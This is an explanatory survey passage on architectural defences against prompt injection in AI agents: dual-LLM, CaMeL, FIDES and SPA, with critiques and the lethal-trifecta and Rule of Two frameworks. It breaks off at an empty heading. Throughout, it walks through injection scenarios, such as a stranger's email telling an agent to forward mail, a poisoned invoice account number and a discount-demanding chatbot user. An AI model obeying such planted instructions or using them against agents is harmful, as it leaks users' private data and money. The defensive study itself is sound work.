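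The second stage needs protection too. It can be ordinary code that tolerates a few false answers, or a model with tools, provided the software first checks that the answers cannot contain instructions, for example by accepting only numbers. In the invoice example, a second model that read the selected files before writing its email would be exposed to the attacker's text again. It has to attach the files without reading them, and preferably without seeing their names, which an attacker may also have chosen. Some tasks can't be divided this way. For example, asking a yes/no question about each of two emails separately cannot establish whether they contradict each other.

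### Two models and a controller

Willison's dual-LLM pattern covers more tasks because the results can be free text. One model, the planner (Willison's "privileged LLM"), takes the user's request and chooses the tool calls. A second, the quarantined model, reads untrusted data but cannot call tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, sits between them. It runs the tools, starts the models and keeps the untrusted text in named variables, showing the planner only the names.

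When a user asks for a summary of the latest email, the planner requests the email, and the controller fetches it and stores it as VAR1. The planner then requests a summary of VAR1. The controller inserts the email's text into the quarantined model's prompt, stores the output as VAR2 and notifies the planner that the summary is ready. The planner writes a reply that includes the name VAR2, and the controller replaces that name with the summary when it displays the reply. An instruction in the email can distort the summary, but the planner never receives the text of the email or the summary.

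Willison lets the planner see the quarantined model's output only when that model has to pick from a fixed set of categories and the controller has checked that the answer is one of them. Any other output stays hidden, even after further models have processed it, because an injection can make a model repeat the malicious instruction in its output.

He described his own solution as "pretty bad". It makes the software more complicated, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the planner undoes the protection. An attacker can also use the displayed summary to try to trick the user into copying private data to a website.

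The CaMeL paper described another weakness of the pattern two years later. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and says that the document's name and Bob's address are in the meeting notes. The planner correctly decides to read the notes, extract both items, fetch the document and send it. But the quarantined model extracts the address from text that an attacker may have edited. If it returns the attacker's address, the controller sends the document there. The system has control-flow integrity but not data-flow security, because the attacker can change a value the plan uses without changing the plan's steps.

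### CaMeL: a program and an interpreter

CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", keeps the two models and adds a record of where each value came from. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, mostly at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich, presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). It is the best-known example of the code-then-execute pattern, in which the planner writes a complete program before any tool runs. For the meeting request, the program might look like this:

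```
emails = read_emails(3)
for email in emails:
    wanted = ask_quarantined("Does this ask for a meeting?", email, yes_or_no)
    if wanted:
        details = ask_quarantined("Extract the event details", email, event)
        create_event(details)
```

The planner writes in a restricted form of Python, chosen because language models already write Python well. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* reports that the restrictions rule out recursion and user-defined functions. A custom interpreter then runs the program one operation at a time, calling the tools and the quarantined model as the program requires.

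The interpreter attaches a tag to each value. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends the system, describes the tag as having two parts. Sources records where the value came from, and Readers records who may see it. A value computed from others inherits their restrictions. In the program above, "details" depends on "email", so anything the quarantined model extracts from the stranger's message counts as coming from the stranger, however harmless it looks.

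Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that checks the arguments and their tags. Willison's example is a request to find Bob's address in the latest email and send him a reminder. The address is untrusted because it comes from an email. The policy for sending mail might allow the call if the address belongs to a known contact and otherwise ask the user. In the meeting-notes example, the same policy would catch the attacker's address, even though the planner never saw it and the injection succeeded against the quarantined model. *CaMeLoT* notes that an injection that reaches the quarantined model can only change the value of a variable. The policy then determines what the program may do with that value.

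Such policies can be very specific, for example requiring that a payment's account number come from the company's own supplier list. But Girrens and Wang (2026) note in *SPA* that the system's security then depends on someone having written a correct and complete policy for every tool. Garby and colleagues also found information flows that CaMeL's interpreter fails to track.

The separation can also help with privacy. The planner's input is only the user's request, so a company that hosts the planner never receives the emails. Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, and Willison suggests that a smaller quarantined model on the user's own computer could do it.

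When agents delegate work to other agents, isolating each one separately is not enough. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes a parent agent whose program inserts a value from a tool into the written instruction for a child agent. The child's planner treats that instruction as coming from its user, so it reads the untrusted value. The paper's interpreter, Multi-CaMeL, makes the parent pass such values in a separate list of variables, whose contents the child's planner doesn't see. If the variables keep their tags, each agent can still enforce a policy that covers the whole group.

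All these systems trust the user's request, which *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) lists among CaMeL's gaps. A user who pastes in text from a website may give the planner an injection directly. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe one more pattern, context minimization, for cases where the user is the attacker. Suppose a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and adds an instruction to offer a huge discount. The system turns the request into a database query, then deletes the request, including the added instruction, from the conversation before the model writes a reply from the query's results.

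### Two meanings of "capability"

The word "capability" in CaMeL's name has an older meaning. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn introduced it in 1966 for an unforgeable token that names an object, such as a file, and grants rights to it. A program needs a token even to refer to a file, and it can read the file only if the token grants that right. The operating system keeps the tokens where programs cannot alter them, so a program cannot give itself new rights.

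Norm Hardy's 1988 paper on the confused deputy shows why isolating untrusted data matters. A compiler had permission to write to a directory that held the company's billing records. Users could choose where the compiler wrote its debugging output, and one user gave the name of the billing file. The compiler overwrote the file, even though the user had no right to change it. With capabilities, the user would have had to supply a token granting access to the output file instead of a name, and the user had no such token for the billing file.

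A capability in CaMeL is a tag on a value that describes the value's history and permitted readers. Unlike a classical capability, which lets the program that holds it do something, the tag gives the program no new rights, and a tool's policy may block the value because of it. In this respect, the tags are closer to the labels that security researchers have used since the 1970s to control where information may go.

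In both ideas, trusted software keeps the record out of reach of the untrusted part, so text in an email cannot change a tag. Both also deal with the confused deputy problem. Hardy's compiler could not distinguish a file that the user had a right to name from one that the user didn't, whereas in CaMeL the sending tool's policy can distinguish an address that the user typed from one that a stranger supplied.

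*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* uses "capability" in a sense closer to the classical one. In its system, TACIT, the program holds the rights, and the compiler checks them. For example, code that an agent writes to process classified text fails the check if it could print, write to a file or use the network. The paper describes CaMeL's tags on data and its own checks on code as complementary.

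### FIDES: labels, hidden values and typed answers

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues developed at Microsoft, protects its planner by controlling what enters the planner's conversation. The planner works in the usual agent loop, choosing one tool call at a time without needing a complete program in advance, and it can read the results that are safe.

Every piece of data has a two-part label that marks its integrity as trusted or untrusted and its confidentiality as public or secret. Information may move only towards more restrictive labels. The least restrictive label is (trusted, public) and the most restrictive is (untrusted, secret). The other two combinations lie between these, and neither is more restrictive than the other. Mathematicians call this kind of ordering a lattice.

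When the system combines two pieces of data, it joins their labels, taking the more restrictive value for each part:

(trusted, secret) ⊔ (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, secret)

In place of "secret" or "public", a label can list the people who may read the data. A join then keeps only those who may read both pieces. If Ann, Bo and Cy may read one document while Bo, Cy and Di may read another, then only Bo and Cy may read a text that draws on both:

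{Ann, Bo, Cy} ⊔ {Bo, Cy, Di} = {Bo, Cy}

Lists of possible writers combine in the opposite way. The join keeps everyone on either document's list, because any of them may have influenced the combined text.

The tools assign the labels. A tool that reads email can list the sender and recipients as the permitted readers and mark the body as untrusted. Different fields of one message can have different labels. For instance, mail servers can authenticate a sender's address, so a developer might mark the address as trusted but not the body.

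The planner's conversation also has a label, which is the join of the labels of everything in it. The system cannot tell which parts of its input influenced a model, so it gives the model's output the label of the whole conversation. This makes a simple labelled agent nearly useless after it has opened one email, because the conversation becomes untrusted and so does every later tool call. FIDES avoids this by hiding any value that would make the conversation's label more restrictive:

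```
when a tool returns a value v with label L:
    if L is no more restrictive than the conversation's label:
        show v to the planner
    else:
        x = a new variable name
        memory[x] = (v, L)
        show the planner x in place of v

when the planner proposes a call f(arguments):
    replace each variable name with its stored value and label
    if the policy allows f with these labels: run f
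    else: refuse the call and report this to the planner
```

FIDES applies the first rule to each field separately, so the planner can see who sent an email while a variable name replaces the body. The planner can pass that variable as an argument in a tool call. In "send VAR1 to Alice", for example, the decision to send and the choice of recipient are trusted, while the text is untrusted. A policy can allow calls like this and still refuse a call whose recipient came from an untrusted source.

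Sometimes the planner needs the contents of a hidden variable to choose its next step. It can reveal the variable, but then the conversation takes on the variable's label. The safer way is to ask a quarantined model a question about the variable and specify the type of answer, such as yes/no or a choice from a list. Constrained decoding forces the answer into that type, although the published evaluation did not use it.

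The answer's label includes its type. FIDES orders types by how much information they can carry, from yes/no values to choices among a few options to free text. A yes/no answer derived from a stranger's email is still untrusted, but it can carry only one bit, which is far too little for an instruction. A policy may therefore let the planner act on that answer but not on untrusted free text. Whoever writes the policy must judge whether to allow this exception.

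The check before each tool call can apply two rules. The integrity rule requires the call, and in its strict form every argument, to come from trusted data. The confidentiality rule requires every recipient to be on the list of permitted readers for whatever the call sends. On its own, the confidentiality rule stops an injection from sending data to people who may not read it, but the injection can still influence the agent. Costa and colleagues combine the rules in two ways. The restrictive combination requires both. The permissive one also allows a disclosure to someone not on the list if the call came from a trusted conversation, on the reasoning that the user must have wanted it.

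### The meeting request in three designs

Suppose Alice has written to the user and Charlie to propose a meeting on Friday at 3 p.m. Charlie has sent the user a private email. The third message is the stranger's instruction to forward mail to an outside address.

A plain agent puts all three emails into its conversation. The stranger's text may then influence every later choice the model makes. It can make the model call the sending tool, choose the recipient, skip Alice's meeting or tell the user there was nothing to do.

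A plan-then-execute agent fixes its plan before reading the emails. It will read them, ask a model whether they contain a meeting request and, if so, create an event with the details the model extracts. Since the plan contains no call to the sending tool, the forwarding attack fails. But one model reads all three emails and fills in every field of the event. A stranger who anticipates this can make the model answer "no", so Alice's meeting never reaches the calendar. Or the stranger can make it answer "yes", list an outside address among the participants and copy Charlie's private email into the description. If the calendar sends invitations, the planned step of creating the event then sends Charlie's email to the outside address.

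In FIDES, the task takes these steps:

1. The planner calls the tool that reads emails. FIDES stores the three bodies as variables, and the conversation stays trusted.
2. For each body, the planner asks a quarantined model whether the email requests a meeting and reveals the yes/no answer.
3. If an answer is yes, the planner asks for the event details from that email. FIDES keeps the details in a new variable.
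4. The planner proposes creating an event with that variable as its argument, and FIDES checks the labels before running the call.

The planner never reads the instruction to forward mail, so the instruction cannot make it propose that call. If the planner revealed the stranger's email in full and followed the instruction, the check would block the call, because the planner's conversation would be untrusted and the outside address would not be on the message's list of readers.

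Because of these labels, it also matters that the planner asks about each email separately. The user, Alice and Charlie may read Alice's email. Only the user and Charlie may read Charlie's, and only the user and the stranger may read the stranger's. Details taken from Alice's email alone can therefore go to Alice and Charlie. If one query covered all three emails, only the user would be allowed to read the result, and the confidentiality rule would block even the invitation Alice asked for.

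The choice of policy matters just as much. Suppose one query does cover all three emails, the policy accepts yes/no answers as safe, and the permissive combination applies. The conversation then counts as trusted, so FIDES treats any disclosure as intended by the user. Yet the stranger's email may have supplied the list of participants, and the invitation could disclose Charlie's private email to them. The restrictive combination would block that call. Costa and colleagues' evaluation used the permissive combination for creating events and the restrictive one for adding participants to existing events, but it didn't use the exception for yes/no answers.

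The table applies to a calendar that sends invitations. Its FIDES entries also depend on separate queries, the exception for yes/no answers, and a particular policy. That policy applies the confidentiality rule and requires a trusted conversation, but allows untrusted event details.

| What the stranger's email can do | Plain agent | Plan-then-execute | FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
| Make the agent call the sending tool | Yes | No | No |
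| Leak a colleague's email through an invitation | Yes | Yes | No |
| Keep Alice's meeting off the calendar | Yes | Yes | No |
| Add an unwanted event | Yes | Yes | Yes |

The unwanted event remains because the user asked for events based on the contents of the emails, and strangers may request meetings. Requiring event details to come from trusted data would prevent it but would also rule out Alice's meeting, since her email is untrusted too.

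### SPA: labels that last from one request to the next

In these examples, the assistant handles only a single request. Girrens and Wang consider agents that keep results and use them later. On Monday, a user asks the agent to find an invoice from Acme and remember the details. The invoice contains an attacker's account number and a malicious instruction. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay the invoice they discussed yesterday. If the planner reads the stored invoice, it is exposed to the malicious instruction. If it doesn't, the payment may still go to the attacker's account.

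SPA deals with the instruction by storing each result as a value, a label and a description. On later requests, the planner sees only the description, which gives the result's type, the request that produced it, and two notes about why the agent ran that step and what the result means. The planner wrote the notes before any tool had run, so text in the invoice could not have influenced them. On Tuesday, the planner can see that Monday's request produced the details of an Acme invoice, and it can write a plan that retrieves and uses them. The value is retrieved only when the plan runs, and it still has Monday's label.

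The planner writes one complete plan per request, in a small language with six kinds of step. A step can retrieve a stored result, call a tool, query a quarantined model, display something to the user, choose between branches, or repeat steps for each item in a list. The language has no arithmetic and doesn't let the planner define functions, so a checker can determine from the plan's text which values each step depends on. The checker examines the whole plan before any tool runs.

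Write C(x) for how secret a value x is and I(x) for how trusted it is. Each tool has a limit on how secret its inputs may be and a minimum for how trusted they must be. Data may flow from s to a destination d only if

C(s) ≤ C(d) and I(s) ≥ I(d)

In both SPA and FIDES, combining trusted with untrusted data gives an untrusted result, although SPA puts trusted data at the top of its integrity scale and FIDES puts untrusted data at the top.

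The checker also takes account of the decisions that led to a step. It keeps a label for the current point in the plan, which starts as the label of the user's request. When the plan branches on a condition, the checker joins the condition's label to the current one and applies the result to every step in both branches:

label of a step = label of the current point ⊔ labels of the step's inputs

In the meeting example, the condition is a yes/no answer from an untrusted email, so every step inside the branch is untrusted, including the one that creates the event. SPA rejects the plan if the calendar tool requires trusted input. FIDES can make an exception for a one-bit answer, but SPA treats that bit like any other untrusted data. Summarizing an untrusted email doesn't make it more trusted either, because the quarantined model's output keeps the label of its input.

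If the checker rejects a plan, the request fails. SPA doesn't send the planner the reason, because with repeated feedback the planner could adjust an unsafe plan until a version passed. SPA is less strict with displayed text, where it blanks out any item the user isn't allowed to see and shows the rest.

A malicious tool could also attack the planner through its own name or description, which most planners read when they choose tools. SPA has an optional mode in which a model infers the tools a task needs from the user's request alone, and the planner writes its plan for these imaginary tools. The system then looks for installed tools that match, but in Girrens and Wang's tests it usually failed to find them.

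On Tuesday, the checker rejects the plan because it would pass an untrusted account number to a payment tool that requires trusted input. It would also reject the plan if the invoice were genuine, because the label records where the number came from, not whether it is correct. Girrens and Wang suggest that future systems could restore trust in a value after an explicit check. For a payment, ordinary code could check the account number against the company's list of approved suppliers.

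## The case that restriction gives up too much and protects the wrong part

SPA would refuse to pay even Acme's genuine invoice, so a customer who wants invoices paid may switch to an assistant that pays them. Critics of restriction expect this to happen wherever the rules get in the way of useful work. Some also argue that the guarantee covers the wrong thing, because it limits the software around the model while much of the harm comes from what the model tells people and how they act on it.

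### Why tools tend to become agents

The argument about usefulness is older than language-model agents. In 2011 Holden Karnofsky suggested that advanced AI could work like Google Maps, which calculates the best route, displays it and leaves the driving to a person. An agent does the same calculation and then acts on the result. Gwern Branwen's essay *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs* argues that agents will outcompete such tools because agents are worth more to their owners and learn better.

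The economic half of the argument uses Amdahl's law, a rule about how much a whole process gains when one part of it speeds up. If a person accounts for a share h of the time a task takes, and the software doing the rest becomes s times faster, the whole task becomes faster by a factor of

1 ÷ (h + (1 − h)/s)

which can never exceed 1/h. Branwen's example is a trading algorithm in which human oversight takes half the time of each decision. However good the algorithm gets, it can at most double its speed. The gain from removing the person also grows as the software improves. Say an assistant takes 30 seconds to prepare an action and its user takes 30 seconds to approve it. Dropping the approval makes the task twice as fast. Once the assistant needs only three seconds, dropping the approval cuts the time from 33 seconds to three, which is eleven times as fast.

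The person's contribution may shrink as well. In "advanced chess", where people play with the help of chess programs, grandmasters at first chose most of the moves themselves, but later players mostly picked from the program's suggestions. By about 2007, according to Branwen, human mistakes increasingly decided games, including clicks on the wrong square. This matters for restricted agents because many of their policies fall back on asking the user.

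Branwen claims that a system learns faster if it can choose what to look at. Suppose a program has to locate a cut-off point on a line to within a thousandth of the line's length. It needs about a thousand examples if they are placed at random, but only ten if it can pick each one itself, because it can then halve the remaining range every time. The Go program AlphaGo reached professional strength by predicting human moves and became superhuman only after playing against itself.

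These cases support unrestricted agents less than they seem to. AlphaGo could only make legal moves on a simulated board, which is a very constrained action space. Most of Branwen's other examples are choices made inside a computation or during training, such as which data to train on, and none of those requires access to outside systems like email. The economic argument is the more serious objection to restricted systems.

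Branwen also gives a short proof that agents are never worse. An agent can always confine itself to giving advice, so its set of possible actions A contains the tool's set T. If U(a) is the value of action a to the owner, then

max U over A ≥ max U over T

Branwen adds the condition that the agent has enough data to learn when acting doesn't help. But the same reasoning gives a second inequality:

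min U over A ≤ min U over T

Every added permission can improve the best available outcome and worsen the worst one. Branwen's proof applies to an agent that chooses well for its owner, whereas designers of isolated systems assume that an attacker may choose the agent's actions.

### The pressure to widen permissions

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues concede that their patterns deliberately prevent an agent from solving arbitrary tasks, and they defend this as a good trade. Their guiding principle is that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action with harmful side effects. Yet people often want an assistant so that incoming messages will trigger actions, such as starting a refund when a customer complains or changing an order when a supplier sends a notice. The patterns also have to be chosen separately for each application, so someone who wants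 one general assistant would get several specialised ones. Four of the six patterns suit an assistant that organises files, but the paper applies only the dual-LLM pattern to a software engineering agent.

Developers may also loosen restrictions after a product is released. Users can complain when a rule blocks their requests, but nobody notices the attacks it prevents, so the product team hears mostly reasons for exceptions. Take the rule that an agent may not send email once it has read a private file. The team might first exempt mail to the company's accountant, then mail to any saved contact, then mail to anyone if the user clicks "OK". The developers can redo the proof after each change, but it guarantees less each time, and eventually it may not rule out the leak that the rule was meant to prevent. Branwen describes a similar loosening in military policy. The Pentagon had insisted that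 a human would always stay in the decision loop for drones, but by 2019 its papers were discussing weapons that people could only audit afterwards.

The companies that train models are under the same pressure. *Aren't AIs just tools?*, an online supplement to the book *If Anyone Builds It, Everyone Dies*, notes that they are trying to make their models act as agents because users want this and it makes business sense. And a restriction on one product doesn't bind anyone else. Zac Hatfield-Dodds, who maintains a widely used software-testing library, points out in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* that a user can ask a tool for the best next action, written as a series of commands for a robot. A program that runs those commands and asks again turns the tool into an agent. A company that only wants to protect its own mailboxes can ignore this, because it has no reason to write that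 program, but it is a serious problem for anyone who hopes that tools will keep dangerous AI contained everywhere.

Branwen expects people to prefer agents unless the agents are considerably worse, and allows that regulation or fear of rare disasters could slow or stop their adoption. An agent that follows instructions from strangers might well count as considerably worse. But when an assistant leaks an email, the person harmed is often the one who wrote it, not the company that chose the assistant. Buyers may therefore undervalue security, and if so, competition will not correct the mistake.

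### Many bounded services

Branwen lists one work that takes the opposite view of the economics, *Reframing Superintelligence* (2019). In it, Eric Drexler, an engineer known for early work on nanotechnology, argues that AI can become fully general as a large collection of services, without any single general agent. In a 2018 talk of the same title, he described a service as doing something that someone wants in bounded time with bounded resources, and his standard example is translation. Customers get generality from the whole collection, which includes services that develop new services. Drexler denies that a general agent would add compelling value, or that competition gives people much reason to hand strategic decisions to AI systems.

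On this view, the buyer of the email assistant loses nothing by getting several specialised assistants, if there are enough of them and they work together. Whether the combined system is still bounded depends on what the bound limits.

Limits on each service's time and spending bound the total only if something limits the number of calls. If each service takes at most one minute of its own and calls up to three others, and calls can nest ten levels deep, the last level alone can contain 3^10 = 59,049 calls, or about 41 days of computing. Without a limit on depth, the total is unbounded even though every service stays within its minute. The total is even harder to cap if services can create new services. Bounds on effects can fail after only two calls, since reading a file and sending an email are enough to leak it. Enforcing either kind of limit requires a mechanism that tracks all the calls,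 such as a shared counter or a monitor with a proved invariant.

Ngo (2019), who had discussed the report with Drexler, doubts in *Comments on Comprehensive AI Services* that the collection of services could compete with a unified agent. Powerful services are hard to make safe individually, and weak ones are hard to combine into a competitive system. Many tasks don't divide neatly. Writing the essay, for example, required Ngo to keep an overall impression of Drexler's views in mind and revise it constantly, and he could not see how separate services would share that work. People could divide a system into modules they understand, but modules and connections that a system learns for itself usually perform better. If any useful computation counts as a service, so does each lobe of a human brain, and calling a system a service no longer implies that it is safe.

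Ngo also worries about the component that decides which services to use. It would need broad knowledge of the world to handle unfamiliar tasks, and it would have to run for a long time to carry out complex plans. Services were supposed to lack both features, and an overseer with its own goal could pursue it through the services. Ngo guesses that Drexler would divide the overseer into bounded services too, which again raises the question of whether the divided version can compete. Companies would also have a motive to remove human intermediaries, since a chief executive who can't improve on an AI system's advice adds nothing by relaying it. According to Ngo, Drexler agrees that this would be dangerous and considers it more relevant than other threats.

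In the isolated designs, the planner is an overseer of this sort. It doesn't have to be narrow, because the monitor checks its calls regardless of what it knows. That gives Drexler's side a better answer than decomposition alone, since one general model can underlie many bounded services. But the monitor bounds only the effects named in the policy. Drexler's report leaves the conditions for avoiding agent-like behaviour in a system of services to further study. In the later *Reframing Superintelligence + LLMs + 4 years*, he accepts that dangerous superintelligent agents could emerge "with relative ease, and perhaps unavoidably". His account shows that generality doesn't require one agent with every permission, but not that a collection of services will stay bounded or that the market will prefer it.

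### Proofs about symbols and harm in the world

Even if customers accepted the restrictions, the proof might leave out most of what they fear. Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, raises this objection against the guaranteed-safety proposal of Dalrymple and colleagues and a related paper by Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro. A mathematical proof is about a system of symbols, so it applies to a real machine only as far as the symbols correctly describe that machine and its surroundings.

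Andrew Dickson's main example is the lander that put the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021. Engineers used a verification tool to show that certain internal faults would not make its software fail. They proved nothing about the landing itself, or about a transistor failing in the computer. Dickson puts the historical failure rate of Mars missions at about half, and cites an analysis that attributes about 20% of the risk to software. If those figures are right, perfect software would lower the failure rate from 50% to about 40%.

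The gap is wider for a chatbot. Suppose its developers want to prove that no reply will spread misinformation. The person who receives a reply might post it online, put it in a speech or email it to anyone, so the developers can't tell whose beliefs they would have to model. They also can't judge the reply by its truth alone, because a genuine photograph can mislead when shown out of context. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' examples include chatbots for medical diagnosis and for questions about medication leaflets. Their context-minimization pattern can delete a malicious request before the model writes its answer, but it can't stop the model from giving the wrong dose.

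Dickson also doubts that anyone could collect the data that precise models need. In 2022 researchers simulated 20 minutes in the life of a single simplified cell, while a human body has about 36 trillion cells. Google's map of a millionth of a human brain took up 1.4 petabytes. Even when a proof exists, someone who uses a chatbot over the internet has no way to check that the model at the other end is the one the proof describes.

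Hatfield-Dodds describes the same difficulty as a series of gaps between the property a developer wants, the specification meant to ensure it, the implementation meant to meet that specification, and the real world where the implementation runs. A proof can close the gap between specification and implementation. In his view, adding a world model only moves the problem, because somebody still has to show that the model matches reality.

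### The published replies

The defenders' main reply is that a model can be useful without being exact. Ammann (2025), in *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, asks only for a sound overapproximation, meaning a model that leaves out nothing the real system might do. Let R be everything that can really happen, M everything the model allows and B the set of bad outcomes. Then

if R ⊆ M and M ∩ B = ∅, then R ∩ B = ∅

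A model that guarantees only that a temperature stays below 50 degrees doesn't predict the exact temperature, but it is enough to prove that a material with a melting point of 60 degrees won't melt. The email rule works the same way. It treats every message sent after a private file has been read as a possible leak, so there is no need to work out which messages actually contain private data.

This answers Dickson's demand for complete physical simulations, but R ⊆ M remains a claim about the world, and no proof inside the model can establish it. Enlarging M makes that claim more likely to be true but makes M ∩ B = ∅ harder to prove. Nora Ammann's own examples show the difficulty. One is a table-tennis robot trained in a simulation that approximates the bat's soft rubber with three extra springs. The approximation was good enough for the robot to beat most human players, but Ammann acknowledges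 that it has no certified error bound. Another is a test for dangerous viruses that would compare each viral protein with each protein on the surface of human cells and reject the virus if any pair could let it enter a cell. The test would also reject some useful gene therapies. Even if it worked perfectly, it would cover only one route to harm, and Dickson had already named another, inserting a sequence directly into human DNA.

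Other replies argue that critics misdescribe what is being proposed. Dickson says the proposal's supporters believe they can guarantee a failure rate of zero. Martinez Suñe, in a comment on Dickson's essay, objects that the specification may instead limit the probability of harm. Omohundro, commenting on Ammann's post, explains that for DNA synthesis machines, a biosafety board would approve a list of sequences, and the proof would show that the machine makes nothing else. The proposal was never to calculate whether a sequence is harmful. Proving that a machine keeps to a list is much easier than proving that a sequence is harmless, but it leaves the judgement about harm to the board, which can be wrong.

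Ammann would deal with errors in the model by monitoring the running system and switching to a backup when observations depart from the predictions. Hatfield-Dodds replied that such monitoring would be pointless if there really were a guarantee. This reply overlooks that the guarantee holds only if the model is correct, which monitoring tests. But monitoring gives no protection if the first sign that the model is wrong is the accident itself.

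Ammann concedes that natural language is so open that specifying safety for chatbots "seems intractable", and says the approach suits areas with settled science, such as electrical grids and supply chains. Hatfield-Dodds complains that advocates cite such closed areas to argue that guarantees are feasible, but cite the dangers of present-day general AI to argue that guarantees are needed. Another commenter asked what fraction of economically valuable work the approach would cover. The objections about harm and usefulness are connected, because defenders can make their guarantees hold by choosing tasks that people can specify, but customers want AI to do other tasks as well.

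### What a narrow claim is worth

Defenders answer that a narrow claim can be useful even if it leaves out most of the danger, as long as it is true. An operator can plan around knowing that no message can reach an outside address, but not around knowing only that the model resisted last month's attacks. Ammann points to seL4, a small operating-system kernel with a full formal proof, and to a US military research programme that used formal methods to remove exploitable bugs. Neither settles what counts as harm, but both stop attacks that depend on the bugs they eliminated.

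As a rough test, this answer works when the proved rule removes a larger share of the expected harm than an unproved defence would. In Dickson's Mars example, the rule removes about 20%, which is useful but modest. For an agent whose worst failure is a payment to the wrong account, a rule about payments might cover nearly all of the harm. The unproved defence's share is less dependable once attackers adapt, but the rule's share also falls if they shift to whatever it leaves out.

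The answer also requires people to remember how narrow the claim is. Branwen observes that the more users trust a tool, the less they check its answers before acting on them. Someone who has heard that an assistant is "provably secure" may read its summaries less carefully, although the proof doesn't cover them. A true claim about forwarding can therefore make a misleading summary more dangerous.

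### What each side predicts

Branwen's argument implies that restriction becomes a greater burden as models improve, because a better model could have done more with the permissions it was denied. Operators would then grant exceptions or switch products. Ammann expects the burden to shrink, since developers can reuse a world model and specification across AI systems, and AI can help to write them. She reports that automated provers went from solving 26% to 63% of the problems in one benchmark within about a year. Dickson accepts that AI will make proofs easier but considers modelling and specification the greater obstacle. Comparing restricted and unrestricted versions of the same agent across successive models would test both forecasts.

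Supporters of isolation predict that a correctly built system will never perform a forbidden action, however inventive the injection. They expect any successful attack to exploit a bug in the trusted software or a policy that failed to forbid the harmful act. Critics can accept this and still predict that total harm will fall very little, because attackers will use permitted channels, such as a false summary or a plausible invoice. Settling the disagreement requires measuring the losses people suffer, because both views are consistent with the same count of blocked actions.

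The sharpest disagreement is about models with goals of their own. Ammann proposes to contain untrusted systems and does not propose to change their goals. She would require a system to submit a solution with proofs that it is correct and unique. The system could then only give that answer or decline, which conveys at most one bit. This works for finding the earliest hour when five people are free, but not for writing a persuasive letter. Critics predict that a misaligned model would do its damage through outputs like the letter, or through a series of permitted steps. One commenter asked Ammann how anybody would build a sound overapproximation of human psychology. Another suggested capping the total number of bits that people receive from the system, but admitted that nobody yet knows a safe limit.

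## The case for partial restriction with layered defences

Most companies that sell agents take a middle position. They remove permissions that users will hardly miss, train the model to ignore instructions in data, run detectors over its inputs or actions, and ask the user to approve the riskier steps. They accept that some attacks will still succeed. An agent built this way can pay a genuine invoice, but its developers can't guarantee that a malicious one will never take control of it.

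The argument for layered defences is that they reduce expected losses. Suppose the model follows 2% of injected instructions, a detector misses a tenth of the resulting actions, and the user approves half of those. If the three failures are independent, one attack in a thousand succeeds. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, discusses an Economist article that recommends this way of thinking, citing Victorian engineers who built in extra strength because they could not be sure of their iron. Willison mostly agrees about ordinary faults but rejects the argument for security, because an attacker will find whatever gap remains. The assumption of independence is also doubtful, since text that makes an action look harmless to the model may also get it past the detector and the user.

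The remaining risk matters more if more people attack. According to a mid-2026 SC Media article sponsored by the security company Sophos, the best-known attacks are still research demonstrations, and no large company has yet suffered a widely publicised disaster. The article also cites a Google study of public web pages, in which malicious injection attempts rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Losses so far may be low because few criminals have tried rather than because the defences are good.

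### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Developers who restrict only part of a system must decide which part. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) names three properties that are dangerous together: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. An attacker can trick an agent that has all three into collecting private data and sending it out. Removing any one of them stops this kind of theft.

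The email assistant has all three, and its mailbox alone supplies the first two. Outside communication includes web requests, images and links as well as email. Willison lists leaks of this kind in more than a dozen products, including ChatGPT, Slack and Microsoft 365 Copilot. The vendors fixed almost all of them quickly, usually by blocking the route the data took out rather than by making the model harder to fool. But users can recreate the combination by connecting tools from different suppliers, and the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for linking agents to tools, makes this easy.

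The trifecta covers only theft of data. An injection can also make an agent delete files or spend money. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) therefore uses a broader set of properties:

- A: the agent can process untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent may have at most two of these within a session. If a task needs all three, a person must approve the agent's actions or the developers must supply another reliable check. This limit is modelled on a rule that Google's Chromium browser project adopted in 2019. Willison (2025), in *Chromium Docs*, explains that browser code may combine at most two of three things: untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe programming language and high privilege.

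Meta applies its rule to an email assistant in three ways. With only B and C, the assistant reads mail only from trusted senders, so the stranger's instruction never reaches the model. With only A and C, it works in a test environment with no real mail to steal. With only A and B, it can read everything but can send mail only to trusted recipients, or after a person has checked the draft. An agent may also change configuration during a session. It could browse the web first and then give up outside communication before it opens internal systems. This change has to be permanent because the web text stays in the agent's conversation and could otherwise make it send out what it reads later.

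Meta's original diagram labelled every pair of properties "safe". In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison (2025) objected that untrusted input combined with the power to change things can do harm even when no private data is involved. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that property B includes every sensitive system, so an agent without B can change only things that don't matter to its user's security. Meta also replaced "safe" with "lower risk". The reply makes the rule consistent, but developers must now decide which systems are sensitive before applying it, and a wrong decision removes the protection.

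Ariel Fogel, a contributor to the security organisation OWASP, made a similar objection at a 2026 conference. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Infosecurity Europe* (2026), Fogel called both frameworks helpful for limiting damage but said that research had already shown attacks working with only two of the properties. With only A and B, for example, the email assistant cannot send anything to the stranger, but the stranger's message can still make it give the user a false summary. Meta says the rule does not cover misinformation of this kind or the agent's own mistakes.

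### What OpenAI has shipped

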